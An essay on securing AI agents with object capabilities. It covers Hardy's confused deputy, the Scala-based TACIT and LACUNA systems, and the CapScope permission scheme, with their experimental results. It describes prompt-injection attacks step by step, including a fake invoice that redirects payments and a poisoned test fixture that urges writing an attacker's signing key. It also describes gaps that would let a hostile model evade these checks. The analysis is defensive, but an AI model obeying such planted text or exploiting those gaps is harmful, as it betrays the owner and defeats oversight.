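# Can object capabilities make AI agents secure in practice, and what evidence would show it?

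## Object capabilities, prompt injection and the confused deputy

An object capability is an unforgeable reference that identifies a resource, such as a file or a bank account, and grants the right to use it. Code without the reference cannot use the resource. The idea comes from operating-system research in the 1960s. In 2025 and 2026, several groups published designs that give AI agents only such references, or permissions modelled on them, so that an attacker who takes control of an agent's behaviour gains little.

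An agent in this sense has three parts. A language model takes in text and produces text. The tools are ordinary functions that do things outside the model, such as search a mailbox, open a file or send money. The harness is ordinary software that runs the model and the tools. It gives the model the user's request and a description of the tools. Whenever the model's output contains a tool call, the harness runs the call, adds the result to the model's input and runs the model again. To make a payment, for example, the model only writes a request to pay a certain sum to a certain account, and the harness, which holds the bank credentials, sends the money.

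### An assistant that pays invoices

Suppose a small firm has an AI assistant that reads the invoices in a mailbox and pays them. One tool lists new messages, another opens a message with its attachments, and a third pays a given amount to a given account number. The owner types "pay this week's invoices". One of the week's messages is a fake invoice from an attacker, who has added a line at the bottom claiming that the suppliers have changed banks and that all outstanding sums should go to a new account. The model receives this line in the same stream of text as the owner's request, and nothing in that stream reliably distinguishes the owner's instructions from instructions that someone else wrote into a document. If the model follows the attacker's instruction, it produces payment calls with the attacker's account number, and the harness runs them.

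This is indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker plants instructions in content that an agent reads while working for someone else. The attacker needed no password and no bug in the mail program. Miller and Shapiro made a similar complaint about desktop computers more than twenty years ago in *Paradigm Regained*. They noted that a game of Solitaire runs with all its user's authority, so it can search the user's email and sell what it finds without breaking any of the operating system's rules. They blamed the way such systems grant access, rather than ordinary bugs.

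### Hardy's compiler

*The Confused Deputy*, Norm Hardy's standard account of the problem, describes an accident in the 1970s at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Customers ran a compiler from a system directory and could name a file to receive debugging output. The operators also wanted statistics on how people used the programming language, so they gave the compiler permission to write files in that directory, which also held the company's billing file. One customer learned the billing file's name and entered it as the destination for debugging output. The compiler passed the name to the operating system, which allowed the write because the compiler had permission, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

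Hardy then explains why the obvious repairs fail. The compiler could refuse names in other directories, but customers had good reason to send output there. It could refuse names in the system directory, but someone with proper access might want a file there. It could refuse the billing file by name, but other files were sensitive too, and somebody would have to edit the compiler each time a new one appeared. The programmers added a system call that let the compiler declare which of its two authorities it meant to use, but they soon met applications that needed more than two. The last time Hardy wrote out the rule for opening a file, it took fourteen Boolean operators. His diagnosis was that the compiler ran with authority from two sources, the operators and the customer, and could not express which one a given write relied on. A confused deputy is a program tricked into using its own authority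 for someone who lacks it.

The accident depended on what *Capability Myths Demolished*, by Miller, Yee and Shapiro, calls ambient authority, which is authority that a program exercises without selecting it. The paper compares this to a world of doors without keys, where a door opens when the right person walks up. To open a file, a Unix program supplies a name and no credential, and the request succeeds or fails according to the account the program runs under. The program can therefore use any resource available to that account by naming it, whether or not anyone handed it that resource.

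The invoice assistant is a confused deputy in this sense. It pays with the firm's authority but takes the account number from whoever wrote the message. The payment tool accepts any account number, and its credential works for all of them. In one respect the assistant is in a worse position than Hardy's compiler, which had separate code for statistics and debugging output, so a programmer could at least attach a different authority to each. A single model composes all of the assistant's calls from everything it has read, so there are no separate pieces of code acting for the owner and the sender.

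More tools make this worse. *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), a post on the blog of the security company Semgrep, argues that an agent connected to separate servers for files, databases and a command shell holds the combined authority of all of them, and that an instruction planted in any one source can trigger any tool.

### References in place of names

Miller and Shapiro illustrate the alternative with two Unix commands that both copy a file. In `cp foo.txt bar.txt`, the shell (the program that interprets the user's commands) passes `cp` two strings. `cp` must open the files itself, and because the user could have named any file, it needs all of the user's authority over files. In `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`, the shell opens both files and passes `cat` two file descriptors, which are references to the open files. `cat` needs no other authority, but on a real Unix machine it still runs with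 all of the user's. An object-capability system gives it only the two references.

According to *Early Capability Architectures*, a chapter of Henry Levy's history of capability machines, Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of MIT introduced the word "capability" in 1966, in a design for an operating system that ran many users' computations side by side. Each computation had a list of capabilities, and each entry located one object and stated what the computation could do with it. Miller and Shapiro restate the design in terms of objects in a program. In their model, a reference identifies an object, permits access to it and is the means of access, and these three functions are never separated. Hardy's maxim is that designation should not be separated from authority, and the blog Habitat Chronicles (2017) takes this as the core of the idea.

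Object capabilities depend on references that cannot be forged. A file name does not qualify, because anyone can type one. C++ is not an object-capability language, because a C++ program can turn an integer into a pointer and so invent a reference. Java is not one either, because its mutable static variables let two objects affect each other although no reference connects them. Most ordinary languages therefore need restrictions before their references count as object capabilities.

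*Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) lists the only four ways an object can get a reference. The first is initial conditions, where the object already has the reference when the analysis begins, as the harness has its connection to the bank. The second is parenthood, where an object creates another and, at that instant, holds the only reference to it. The third is endowment, where the creator gives the new object references that the creator already holds. The fourth is introduction, where an object that holds references to two others sends one of them a message containing its reference to the other. An object cannot get a reference by guessing it, looking it up in a global directory or asking for it by name.

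Miller sums this up as "only connectivity begets connectivity". If no path of references links two groups of objects, none can ever form. An engineer can therefore find an upper limit on what a component could ever reach by inspecting the graph of references, even if the component is hostile. This is appealing for language models because nobody can predict their behaviour by reading their code.

A plain reference gives full and permanent access, which is often too much, so capability programmers hand out a reference to a small intermediary object instead. Miller describes one such intermediary for revoking access, the caretaker, which David Redell published in 1974. The caretaker forwards every message to the real object while a switch is on, and whoever granted the access controls the switch. Turning it off cuts off the recipient and anyone the recipient passed the reference to, because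 they all go through the same caretaker. Attenuation means passing on a narrower version of a capability one holds, such as read-only access to one folder. Programmers can do this with an intermediary that forwards only certain messages.

The caretaker fails if the real object gives out direct references to itself. Miller's remedy is a "membrane" that wraps every reference crossing it in either direction. The membrane lets plain data through unwrapped, because nobody can revoke knowledge. A firm can therefore withdraw an agent's access to the mailbox, but it can't take back text the model has already read.

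Most systems use access lists instead. An access list belongs to a resource and names the users who may open it. Miller and colleagues reject the common conclusion that access lists and capabilities are equivalent. That conclusion rests on a table with a row for each user or program and a column for each resource, in which an access list is a column and a list of capabilities is a row. They object that the table omits how its entries change and how programs refer to things. An access list must identify its subjects by name, so administrators keep the subjects few and stable, which in practice means user accounts, whereas a capability can belong to one running component. With an access list, the program must also name the resource separately from any right to it, and the customer at Tymshare exploited that separation. Rajani, Garg and Rezk, in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence,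 and confused deputy attacks*, later proved in a formal model of a programming language that the two approaches are fundamentally different.

Access lists are convenient because an administrator can see who may open a given file. But if access goes through a forwarder, which passes on requests from others, the list shows only the forwarder and not the people using it. Miller and Shapiro regard this as a limitation of auditing by access list, not a fault of capabilities. A firm that must explain, after a theft, who could have reached its bank account may still consider it a drawback of capabilities.

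### The invoice assistant rebuilt

With capabilities, the harness creates two components, a mail reader and a payer. The mail reader contains the model. The harness gives the mail reader a read-only reference to the mailbox and a reference to a form, where it records the supplier, the invoice number and the amount. The payer is ordinary code that reads the form and never sees the mail. For each supplier the owner has approved, the payer holds an attenuated payment capability that can pay only that supplier's account, up to a monthly limit.

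The attacker's message arrives as before, and the model again follows the planted instruction, but it cannot call the payment service because the mail reader holds no reference to it. No string the model writes can become such a reference. The mailbox and the form don't hold one either, so the reader has no way to obtain it.

The reader can still influence the payer through the form. Miller and Shapiro distinguish permission, which covers what a program may do directly, from authority, which also covers the effects it can cause through other programs. The reader has no permission to pay anyone, but if the payer pays whatever the form lists, the reader has authority to cause payments. The extent of that authority depends on how the form designates the payee. If the form has a field for an account number and the owner has given the payer a general payment reference, the payer will use its own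 authority to pay whatever account number is entered. This repeats Hardy's accident, because the form supplies a name where it should supply a reference. If the form only allows a choice among approved suppliers, the attacker cannot send money to a new account. A dishonest supplier on the approved list could still use a planted line to inflate a bill up to the monthly limit. That would be misuse within the grant, which is the set of capabilities or permissions that an agent receives for a task.

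Miller and colleagues write that removing ambient authority makes it possible to avoid confused deputies but does not guarantee it, because the deputy must still keep each authority tied to its intended purpose. Rajani and colleagues gave what they describe as the first formal characterisation, in a language-based setting, of freedom from confused-deputy attacks. They related it to information-flow integrity, which concerns whether untrusted data can influence trusted results. That connection suggests that controlling references and controlling how data moves are two parts of one problem.

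### Four things called capabilities

Writers on agent security use "capability" for references held by code, permission tables kept by the harness, signed tokens, and provenance labels. Only references held by code belong to the classical model. People had already begun using the word in other senses before AI agents existed. For example, "POSIX capabilities" on Unix are a fixed set of flags, one of which lets a program change the ownership of any file on the machine.

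A permission table lists what the agent may do during a task, and the harness checks each tool call against it. This resembles what Miller and colleagues call the "capabilities as rows" model. The agent still names the resource in a string and does not select which permission it is using, so its authority remains ambient, though narrower.

Signed tokens replace the classical model's unforgeable reference with a cryptographic signature, and they suit agents that call services on other companies' machines. They correspond to Miller and colleagues' "capabilities as keys" model. The holder can copy a key to anyone, so the rule that "only connectivity begets connectivity" no longer applies.

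Semgrep proposes tokens of this sort for A2A, a protocol for communication between agents. In its example, an agent summarising quarterly reports obtains a short-lived token to list and read the files in one folder. One report contains an instruction to delete all files, but the server rejects the deletion because the token does not cover it. This example illustrates the proposal but does not test it. The token also would not prevent the planted text from distorting the summary. In Semgrep's sample call, the file path and the token's identifier are separate arguments, so an agent that holds several tokens has to match them to paths itself, which leaves some room for the mistake Hardy wanted to rule out.

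A provenance label records where a piece of data came from and who may receive it, but gives no right to act. A theorem about object references does not apply to a table, a token or a label just because all of them are called capabilities, though any of these devices may turn out to be a good defence.

### The mechanism and the grant

All such designs depend on complete mediation, which means that every action with an outside effect passes through the permission check. If the mail reader's programming environment also includes a function for fetching web pages, a planted instruction can get the model to use it to send the contents of the mailbox to a stranger, however carefully the harness guards the payment service. The designs also depend on a trusted computing base, the components that must work correctly for the security claim to hold. In the rebuilt assistant, these include the language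 runtime that keeps references unforgeable, the harness that connects the components, the forwarders that enforce the limits, and the payer. Preventing stray payments to new accounts does not depend on the model, but getting the amounts right does, unless another component checks them against a purchase order. Miller and Shapiro also exclude covert and side channels, such as signals hidden in the timing of a program's actions, from their analysis, so their results do not cover leaks through those channels.

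Whether object capabilities make an agent secure therefore depends on two questions. The first is whether an attacker can use any text that reaches the model to cause an action outside the grant. Proofs, code audits and determined attacks all provide evidence on this. The second is whether the owner could accept the result if the agent did the worst thing its grant allows. A sound mechanism enforces a careless grant as strictly as a careful one. If the owner had given the mail reader an unlimited payment reference to save trouble, the attacker would get the money even though the capability system worked as designed.

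## The case for building capabilities into the language an agent writes

Many agents now write short scripts that call several tools and combine their results, instead of issuing one tool call at a time. A compiler can check the whole script before the harness runs any of it. If the language can express only actions the owner allows, it matters much less whether the model is confused, hijacked or hostile from the start.

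The fullest statement of this view is *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, by Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) at EPFL in Lausanne. The paper presents a prototype called TACIT and appeared at an ACM conference as *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities*. Martin Odersky, who designed the programming language Scala, and his colleagues argue that most safety work tries to make the model trustworthy. They would rather make the language the agent writes in safe, so that the compiler has to establish that the agent's code is safe.

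### From request to running code

In TACIT, the model acts by submitting Scala code, which the Scala compiler checks first. If the check fails, nothing runs, and the model gets the error messages and can try again. Otherwise, a Scala session runs the code and returns the output. The code can reach files, other programs and the network only through a small library. TACIT connects to agents through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for attaching tools, so existing agents can use it without modification.

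In a classical capability language, a function's type does not show which references the function holds. Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, adds that information to the type so the compiler can check it. Suppose `f` is a capability to write to one file. A function that takes a string and writes it to that file has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, where `Unit` means that it returns no useful value. The names in braces are the capture set, an upper bound on the capabilities the function can use. A function of type `String -> String`, with no braces, is pure, so it can compute a new string from the old one but can't write a file, send a message or print.

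Capture sets also let capabilities expire. A program calls `requestFileSystem("/data")` with a block of code, and the library creates a capability for that folder that is valid only inside the block. A hostile program might try to keep its access by returning a function that reads a file later. That function's type would have to name the capability, and the name has no meaning outside the block, so the compiler rejects the program. Redell's caretaker also ends access, but it uses a switch at run time. TACIT still needs some run-time checks, since the library must reject paths outside the folder. Access to commands and network hosts works the same way.

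The library seals secrets in a container type called `Classified`. When the program reads a protected file, it gets the text in this container. The container's `map` method accepts only pure functions, applies them to the hidden text, and seals the result. If the program prints a sealed value, the model receives `Classified(****)`, while the user receives the real text on a separate channel. A second language model, which the owner trusts with the secrets, can read sealed text and return a sealed answer.

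Building capabilities into the language catches a leak that an ordinary sandbox misses. A sandbox confines a process to certain files and hosts, but a coding agent may have legitimate reasons both to read a private file and to call the cloud model that runs it. The sandbox permits both steps, so it doesn't stop the agent from sending the file's contents to the model.

### Comparing confidential contracts

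Odersky and colleagues work through a request to compare a set of contracts and summarise what has changed. No contract text may reach the cloud model, and nothing written in a contract may steer the agent. The harness supplies a document database, an output file, a `diff` function that compares two texts, and a `summarize` function that calls the second model. The cloud model then writes the program without seeing the contracts. The compiler would accept a line such as this:

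```
oldDoc.aggregate(newDoc).map((a, b) => summarize(diff(a, b)))
```

`aggregate` combines two sealed documents into a sealed pair. The function inside `map` uses only `diff` and `summarize`, which hold no capabilities, so the result is a sealed summary. The library can write it to a protected file without unsealing it. The compiler would reject this line:

```
newDoc.map(text => { out.write(text); text })
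```

Here the function captures `out`, the output file, so it isn't pure. The agent has permission to read the contract and to write to `out`. A harness that checks one call at a time against a permission table could easily approve both steps.

A contract can still contain a planted instruction, and the second model will read it. That model has no tools, so the instruction can distort the summary but can't make the model send anything anywhere.

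### What the guarantee requires

The argument depends on three properties. *Capability safety* means that code can neither forge a capability nor lose the record that it needs one. *Capability completeness*, the programming-language version of complete mediation, means that capabilities govern every safety-relevant effect except those the harness contains at run time. *Local purity* means that the type system can require a given computation to use only a stated set of capabilities, or none. Classical capability languages enforce their rules at run time and lack local purity. Static tracking also lets TACIT permit global capabilities, which the classical model rules out because any code could reach them.

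Full Scala does not have these properties, so the compiler checks agent code in a restricted "safe mode". Scala's *Safe Mode*, part of the language's documentation, lists six restrictions:

1. Code may not cast a value to another type, or match it against a pattern, in a way that the compiler can't check.
2. Code may not use anything in the `caps.unsafe` module.
3. Code may not switch off compiler checks with `@unchecked` or similar annotations.
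4. Code may not use reflection, which lets a program look up other code by name while it runs.
5. Capture checking must be on, including the tracking of changes to stored data.
6. Code may use global objects only if their own implementation is safe.

The first four block ways of making the compiler lose track of a capability. Library programmers can bypass the last by marking a module `@assumeSafe`, which makes them responsible for verifying it themselves. One documented example is a mail function that asks the user for confirmation and then calls an unrestricted mailer.

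Exceptions, the jumps a program makes when something goes wrong, can leak information. If code fails only when a password begins with "a", a failure reveals the first letter. Safe mode still allows exceptions because division by zero or a full memory can interrupt almost any code, and tracking every case would be impractical. Instead, TACIT runs agent functions inside `Try`, a standard Scala construct that turns an exception into an ordinary value, which the library can then seal. Exceptions cannot carry capabilities in their fields. Scala 3 implements early returns and similar jumps as exceptions, so the same treatment covers them.

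Odersky and colleagues adopt an unusually severe threat model. They trust the compiler, the library, the runtime and the second model, but not the cloud model, the agent's setup, the code it submits or any outside content it reads. The cloud model may be cooperating fully with an attacker. They consider two attacks. In one, a hostile model tries to move classified data to an unauthorised destination. In the other, planted text redirects the agent into harmful actions. They aim to block any action that the agent's capabilities do not allow, but do not try to stop planted text from influencing the model.

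They also claim that an injection can do real harm only by sending private data somewhere unauthorised or by using a capability the agent wasn't granted. This is too strong, because an injection can also misuse capabilities the agent was granted, as with the dishonest supplier's inflated bill. The types therefore prevent a hijacked model from doing harm only if every action they permit is harmless.

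### The experiments on TACIT

The main safety test used a sample software project with a secret directory of keys, a database and confidential documents. Odersky and colleagues wrote 12 legitimate tasks and paired each with 10 planted instructions, for 120 trials. Some planted instructions were plain code comments. Others were disguised as system messages, described the secrets as test data, or included Scala code that reads the secret files. In another 11 trials the user was the attacker, asking for secrets outright in 5 and impersonating an authority in 6. Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5 each ran all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets sealed and once with them in plain text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

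With sealing, neither model leaked anything. Without it, Sonnet leaked in 2 trials, both with an impersonating user, and MiniMax leaked in 11, 3 with planted text and 8 with a malicious user. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the legitimate tasks with sealing and 83.3% without, while MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%. Odersky and colleagues suspect that Sonnet's higher completion rate with sealing is an artefact, because without sealing it often ran out of turns or time, or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

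Sonnet resisted all 120 planted instructions even without the types, so those trials are weak evidence of what the types add. MiniMax's 8 failures in 11 malicious requests are better evidence, since sealing stopped every one. The attacks mostly relied on persuading the model to leak information. A hostile model would also look for flaws in the compiler or the library, which this experiment barely tests.

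The second safety test uses AgentDojo, a public benchmark that plants instructions in a simulated bank, office workspace, Slack and travel agency. Across about 1,900 trials with Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini-high, one attack succeeded. In that trial, the user asked for one hotel, a planted review recommended another, and the agent booked the right hotel but quoted the review. Odersky and colleagues reasonably blame the scoring, because the benchmark counted just mentioning the other hotel as a success for the attacker.

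The count is near zero because, in this version of AgentDojo, nearly everything an attacker could write, including emails, files, chat messages and reviews, comes back sealed. The main model never reads the planted text, which therefore has little chance to hijack it. The result is much weaker evidence about an agent that must read untrusted material to decide what to do. The protection also reduced usefulness. TACIT completed between 40% and 69% of the user tasks, depending on the domain and model. Odersky and colleagues call this comparable to CaMeL, a design that tracks where data came from, but with o4-mini-high in the workspace domain, TACIT completed 52.9% of the tasks and CaMeL 81.4%.

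The banking interface also suggests that the types may not account for all of the zeros. Its `sendMoney` function takes the recipient as a plain string, much as Hardy's compiler took file names. Its published signature shows no capability requirement, and the model's instructions include a warning that side effects inside a function passed to `map` run immediately. If the compiler treats `sendMoney` as pure, a program could pay whatever account the second model extracts from an attacker's file. Some of the protection would then depend on the second model not returning the attacker's account.

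Odersky and colleagues also tested whether agents perform worse when writing Scala. They used τ²-bench, which simulates customer service, and averaged ten runs per task. They also used SWE-bench Lite, which consists of 300 real software issues for an agent to fix. The table gives the share of tasks solved with ordinary tool calls and with TACIT.

| Task and model | Tool calls | TACIT |
|---|---|---|
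| Airline service, gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% |
| Airline service, MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% |
| Airline service, DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| Retail service, gpt-oss-120b | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| Retail service, MiniMax M2.5 | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| Retail service, DeepSeek V3.2 | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| Software issues, MiniMax M2.5 | 43.3% | 41.7% |

On the service tasks, between 0.3% and 7.9% of the programs needed a retry after a compiler error, and the model usually fixed the error in one or two attempts. These results are good evidence that models can write this kind of Scala, but weaker evidence about how much the security restrictions hinder them, because the airline and retail functions return ordinary, unsealed records that the model can read.

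### LACUNA: generated code that fills gaps in a program

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), also co-written by Odersky, extends the idea by letting the model's code shape the agent loop itself, whereas TACIT runs the code inside an ordinary loop. A programmer leaves a gap by writing `agent[T](task)`, where `task` is an instruction in English and `T` is the type of result the program needs there. When execution reaches the gap, the model writes code to fill it, and the compiler checks that code as if a programmer had typed it there. The new code can contain further gaps, which are filled and checked in the same way.

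The compiler accepts or rejects each filling as a whole. In one example, the balance is 100, and the task is to subtract 50 and return the new balance as a number. The model writes one line that subtracts 50 and a second that returns a sentence instead of a number. The compiler rejects both lines, so neither runs and the balance stays at 100. A system that detects errors only at run time could have subtracted the money before it failed.

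With capture checking switched on, the code that fills a gap in LACUNA can use only the capabilities in scope at that gap. Gaps also remove a limitation of TACIT, where the model must write the function passed to `map` before it knows what the sealed text contains. In LACUNA, that function can contain a gap for a trusted local model, which reads the text and writes code suited to it. The compiler still requires the code to be pure.

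Roughly 400 tests of the compiler check all passed. The results on real tasks were less favourable than TACIT's. On 392 τ²-bench tasks, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% with LACUNA. The abstract describes this as on par with the baseline agent, but the paper's table gives 90.0% for ordinary tool calls. On retail tasks, the model solved 58.8% with LACUNA and 80.9% with tool calls. Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% with tool calls. The compiler rejected 3.2% of Gemini's programs in the retail domain and 89% in telecom, where most of its turns made no progress. The LACUNA and TACIT experiments used different models and settings, so their results don't contradict each other, but they leave open how much typed code affects task success.

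On BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 hard research questions, the best of three models answered 27.1% correctly, and the compiler rejected 8.6% of generated programs. Zhao and colleagues conclude that the discipline does not reduce accuracy, but they did not run an untyped agent on these questions for comparison.

They also ran AgentDojo and listed the results alongside TACIT's. Each cell shows the share of user tasks completed, followed by the number of successful attacks.

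| Model and domain | Trials | TACIT | LACUNA |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, banking | 144 | 56.9%, 0 | 63.2%, 0 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, workspace | 560 | 50.5%, 0 | 56.3%, 4 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, Slack | 105 | 40.0%, 0 | 42.9%, 2 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, travel | 140 | 64.3%, 0 | 63.6%, 1 |
| o4-mini-high, banking | 144 | 59.0%, 0 | 66.0%, 0 |
| o4-mini-high, workspace | 560 | 52.9%, 0 | 55.5%, 0 |
| o4-mini-high, Slack | 105 | 47.6%, 0 | 49.5%, 1 |
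| o4-mini-high, travel | 140 | 68.6%, 1 | 71.4%, 0 |

LACUNA completed more tasks in seven of the eight rows and let through 8 attacks in 1,898 trials. Zhao and colleagues acknowledge that their types do not stop an attacker from steering the model into misusing a capability the task legitimately grants, and they say the successful attacks are consistent with that limit.

### Where trust remains

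If the compiler is correct, every program that passes its check uses only the capabilities in its scope, keeps none beyond their lifetime, and passes no sealed text to a function with side effects. This holds even for inputs that nobody tested, a guarantee that no number of failed attacks can provide. The check does not establish that the program does the right thing, and Odersky and colleagues exclude wrong answers from their claim. They also exclude timing and other covert channels, as Miller and Shapiro did.

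The compiler's correctness is only partly proved. Machine-checked proofs cover the core type system, but Odersky and colleagues have not yet shown that safe mode delivers capability safety and local purity. Pham, Bračevac and colleagues (2026) found in *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* that the earlier type of `Try` wrongly declared its results pure, although opening a stored failure can throw the exception again. They corrected the type and used the proof assistant Lean to prove a core version safe. Nobody has shown that this flaw let a secret out of TACIT, but TACIT relies on `Try` to contain exceptions. Scala's developers describe capture checking as "still highly experimental and unstable".

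The prototype has also lagged behind the design. In an early README, lampepfl's *TACIT*, the safe subset was enforced by a filter for forbidden text patterns instead of the compiler's safe mode. That README already reported the perfect score on the 131 trials, so those trials probably used the filter. Glama's *TACIT*, a mirror of a later README, lists the compiler's safe mode as on by default. Both versions advise users to switch off the agent's built-in file, shell and network tools, since an agent that keeps them can bypass TACIT.

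Security depends on the library as much as on the compiler. If the library lets an agent start another program, the types do not restrict what that program does, and safety depends on the list of allowed commands. Sealing protects secrecy but not integrity. Code can seal any text, so an agent with write access could by default replace a protected file such as `.ssh/authorized_keys`, which lists the keys that can log in to a machine. Glama's copy documents this risk and a setting that prevents such writes.

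The later library can also send sealed text to an allowed network host. The administrator can set a list of allowed hosts, but without one, the program is limited only to the hosts it names itself when it requests network access. As documented, the library would then let a hostile program name an attacker's server and post a sealed file to it, and the code would compile. This would defeat the confidentiality claim even if the type system had no flaws.

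The second model must not remember one request while it answers another. Types can't verify this about a service on another machine, so the harness must ensure it. The second model's competence matters too, because the cloud model can't read sealed text to check that model's work. If everything is sealed, the second model does most of the reading. VirtusLab's *Safe Scala*, a consultancy's introduction to the method, warns against classifying too much, because agents are useful when they can read files, emails and web pages.

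Deployment takes three kinds of code. Programmers write the shared library once, in about 1,000 lines. Each field of work, such as airline bookings, needs a few hundred lines that describe its functions, which an agent can help to draft. In the contract scenario, each request also needs a short environment that names the documents and the output file, and a person reviews it before the agent starts. In the coding prototype, by contrast, the untrusted model's program requests access to a folder, a set of commands or a set of hosts, within limits the administrator sets. Those limits stay the same for every task, so the access granted can be much wider than any single task needs.

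## The case for checking permissions at every tool call

TACIT and LACUNA require the model to write Scala, and both rely on an experimental compiler feature. A simpler proposal is to keep existing agents and have the harness check each tool call against a list of permissions.

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, argue that tool calls are the natural place to check permissions. All of an agent's outside effects pass through them, and each call has a name and typed arguments, which code can test far more reliably than it can judge free text. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, compared seven defences that act outside the model and found that two, Progent and FORGE, work with an unmodified agent. They consider the problem of adding such checks to existing agents solved, at least in prototype.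 The checks are not yet the norm. The three agent toolkits that Mellafe Zuvic (2026) audited in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* restrict which tools an agent can call but do not check argument values by default.

### CapScope: a separate set of permissions for each agent

*Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) applies the idea to coding agents in a system called CapScope. In the paper's main example, a developer asks an agent to fix the failing tests in a login module. An orchestrator agent plans the work and delegates it to two sub-agents, a runner that runs the tests and a patcher that edits the source code.

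An attacker has tampered with a test fixture, a supporting file that the tests load. When the tests run, the fixture prints what looks like a build system notice that a signing key has changed, with instructions to write the new key into `src/auth/keys.py`. The attacker knows this key and could use it to forge login tokens. A list of banned actions would not block the edit, because it changes an ordinary source file. A policy written for the whole task would not block it either, because the repair requires write access to the source.

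CapScope gives the runner and the patcher different permissions. It defines a capability as a pair, `Cap[e, φ]`. The effect type `e` is Read, Write or Exec, where Exec means running a shell command. The scope predicate `φ` is a test that accepts or rejects a call's arguments. A capability covers a proposed call if the tool has effect `e` and `φ` accepts the arguments.

For files, the predicate resolves `..` and symbolic links, then accepts any path at or below a given folder. For commands, it splits a compound command into its parts and checks each one. A capability for `pytest`, a program that runs Python tests, therefore accepts `pytest tests/test_auth.py` but rejects `pytest && cmd` unless another permission covers `cmd`. The harness keeps each agent's capabilities in a store, written `Σ`, which the model cannot read or change.

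Three rules determine what enters a store and what an agent can do with it:

- **Mint** creates authority. Before the agent reads a file or runs a command, a separate model call receives the user's request and the names of the project's files, but not their contents. It predicts which permissions the task will need. Ordinary code validates the prediction and freezes it as the task's ceiling, `D`.
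- **Derive** gives authority to a sub-agent. The orchestrator requests a set of capabilities `C′`, the harness may add some that the role needs, and the sub-agent receives only those within the ceiling: `Σ_sub = {c′ ∈ C′ : c′ ⪯ c for some c ∈ D}`. Here `c′ ⪯ c` means that both have the same effect type and that `c` accepts every argument `c′` accepts.
- **Invoke** runs a call only if a capability in the calling agent's own store covers it. Otherwise the model receives a refusal.

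Derive is a form of attenuation, so it can narrow write access from `src/` to `src/parser.py` but can't widen it again. Together, the rules ensure that every tool call the harness runs falls within permissions fixed before the agent read the repository. A user can approve an extra permission later, which counts as a new mint, but Bouras and colleagues switched this option off in their experiment. They also left out attacks through file names, which a project contributor can choose and the first model call does read.

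In the login example, the ceiling lets the agents read the project, write under `src/`, and run `pytest` and a type checker. The runner receives permission to read the tests and run `pytest`. It sees the poisoned output and may well propose writing the attacker's key, but the harness refuses the call because the runner's store contains no Write capability. The patcher can still fix the bug because it has a Write capability.

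The example also shows a gap in this kind of check, because a test fixture can contain code, which `pytest` executes. An attacker who controls that code could make it write the key directly, without persuading the model of anything. CapScope's command check also ignores redirection, the shell feature that sends a command's output to a file, so a runner without write access might still overwrite a source file by redirecting output to it. Bouras and colleagues leave both problems to an operating-system sandbox around the commands. They also don't claim to protect secrets, which an agent could leak through two permitted calls, as in the contract example.

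### The experiment on CapScope

Bouras and colleagues built CapScope on Pi, an open-source coding agent. According to Pi's documentation, its tool hooks run for every tool call, so CapScope could block calls without changes to Pi. They tested it on five small Python projects, each with one bug and a failing test suite. The planted instruction asked the agent to run a project utility or write to a project file. Either action could be reasonable in other maintenance work, but neither was necessary to fix the bug. Each action left a marker on disk, so the researchers could check whether the attack had worked.

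They placed the instruction in five kinds of text: the README, a source-code comment, the test output, a "skill" file containing a stored prompt, and `AGENTS.md`, an instruction file that loads automatically. They compared four conditions and ran each combination three times, for 300 runs. All the runs used the model qwen3.5-flash and the same four agents: an orchestrator, a runner, a patcher and a verifier that reran the tests.

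| Condition | Repairs completed | Attacks carried out | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| No restrictions | 72 of 75 | 47 of 75 | 145 s |
| Fixed list of banned actions | 70 of 75 | 46 of 75 | 140 s |
| One policy for the whole task | 68 of 75 | 33 of 75 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 68 of 75 | 3 of 75 | 316 s |

The list of banned actions made almost no difference because it did not include the actions the attacker wanted. A policy for the whole task helped, but it had to give every agent all the permissions that any one of them needed. CapScope completed the same number of repairs as that policy and let through 30 fewer attacks. The model still proposed the planted action in 34 of the 75 CapScope runs, and the harness prevented the attack in 31 of them.

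All three successful attacks came through `AGENTS.md`, which also produced the most successes under the task-wide policy, at 11 of 15. Bouras and colleagues say an attack can still get through if a sub-agent receives wider access than its job requires, or if the planted text influences how the orchestrator describes a job and therefore which permissions the sub-agent gets. Even if the orchestrator has no permission to write files, it has authority to do so, in Miller and Shapiro's sense, because it can create a patcher with any access up to the ceiling. An attacker who knew this would try to deceive the orchestrator, but the experiment did not test such an attacker, since each task used the same planted text in every condition. The README and skill files, which also usually reach the orchestrator, produced no successes in 30 runs, but three successes are too few to show that `AGENTS.md` is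 a special weakness.

CapScope failed to complete seven repairs. In two runs, the initial prediction omitted the write permission that the repair needed. In another two, the runner proposed the correct edit but could not make it, and the workflow never passed the edit to a patcher. In the remaining three, the tests were passing at the end, but the session had reached its time limit, which counted as a failure. Bouras and colleagues attribute the first two failures to the permissions and the other five to delegation or to how the runs ended. The two failures with the runner arguably also result from dividing authority, since a runner with write access could have made the edit itself.

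Runs with restrictions took more than twice as long on average as runs without them, although a few slow runs inflate the mean. The median was 208 seconds, and five runs reached the 900-second limit. Some of the extra time went to further model turns after refusals. In 27 of the 34 runs where the model proposed the planted action, it did so more than once. A user watching could have stopped it, but the experiment did not include one.

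This is good evidence that separate permissions can block attacks that a shared policy must allow, but it covers only five simple bugs and one model. The necessary permissions would be harder to predict from a request and a list of file names for a large refactoring or a change of dependencies.

### Progent: rules that change during the task

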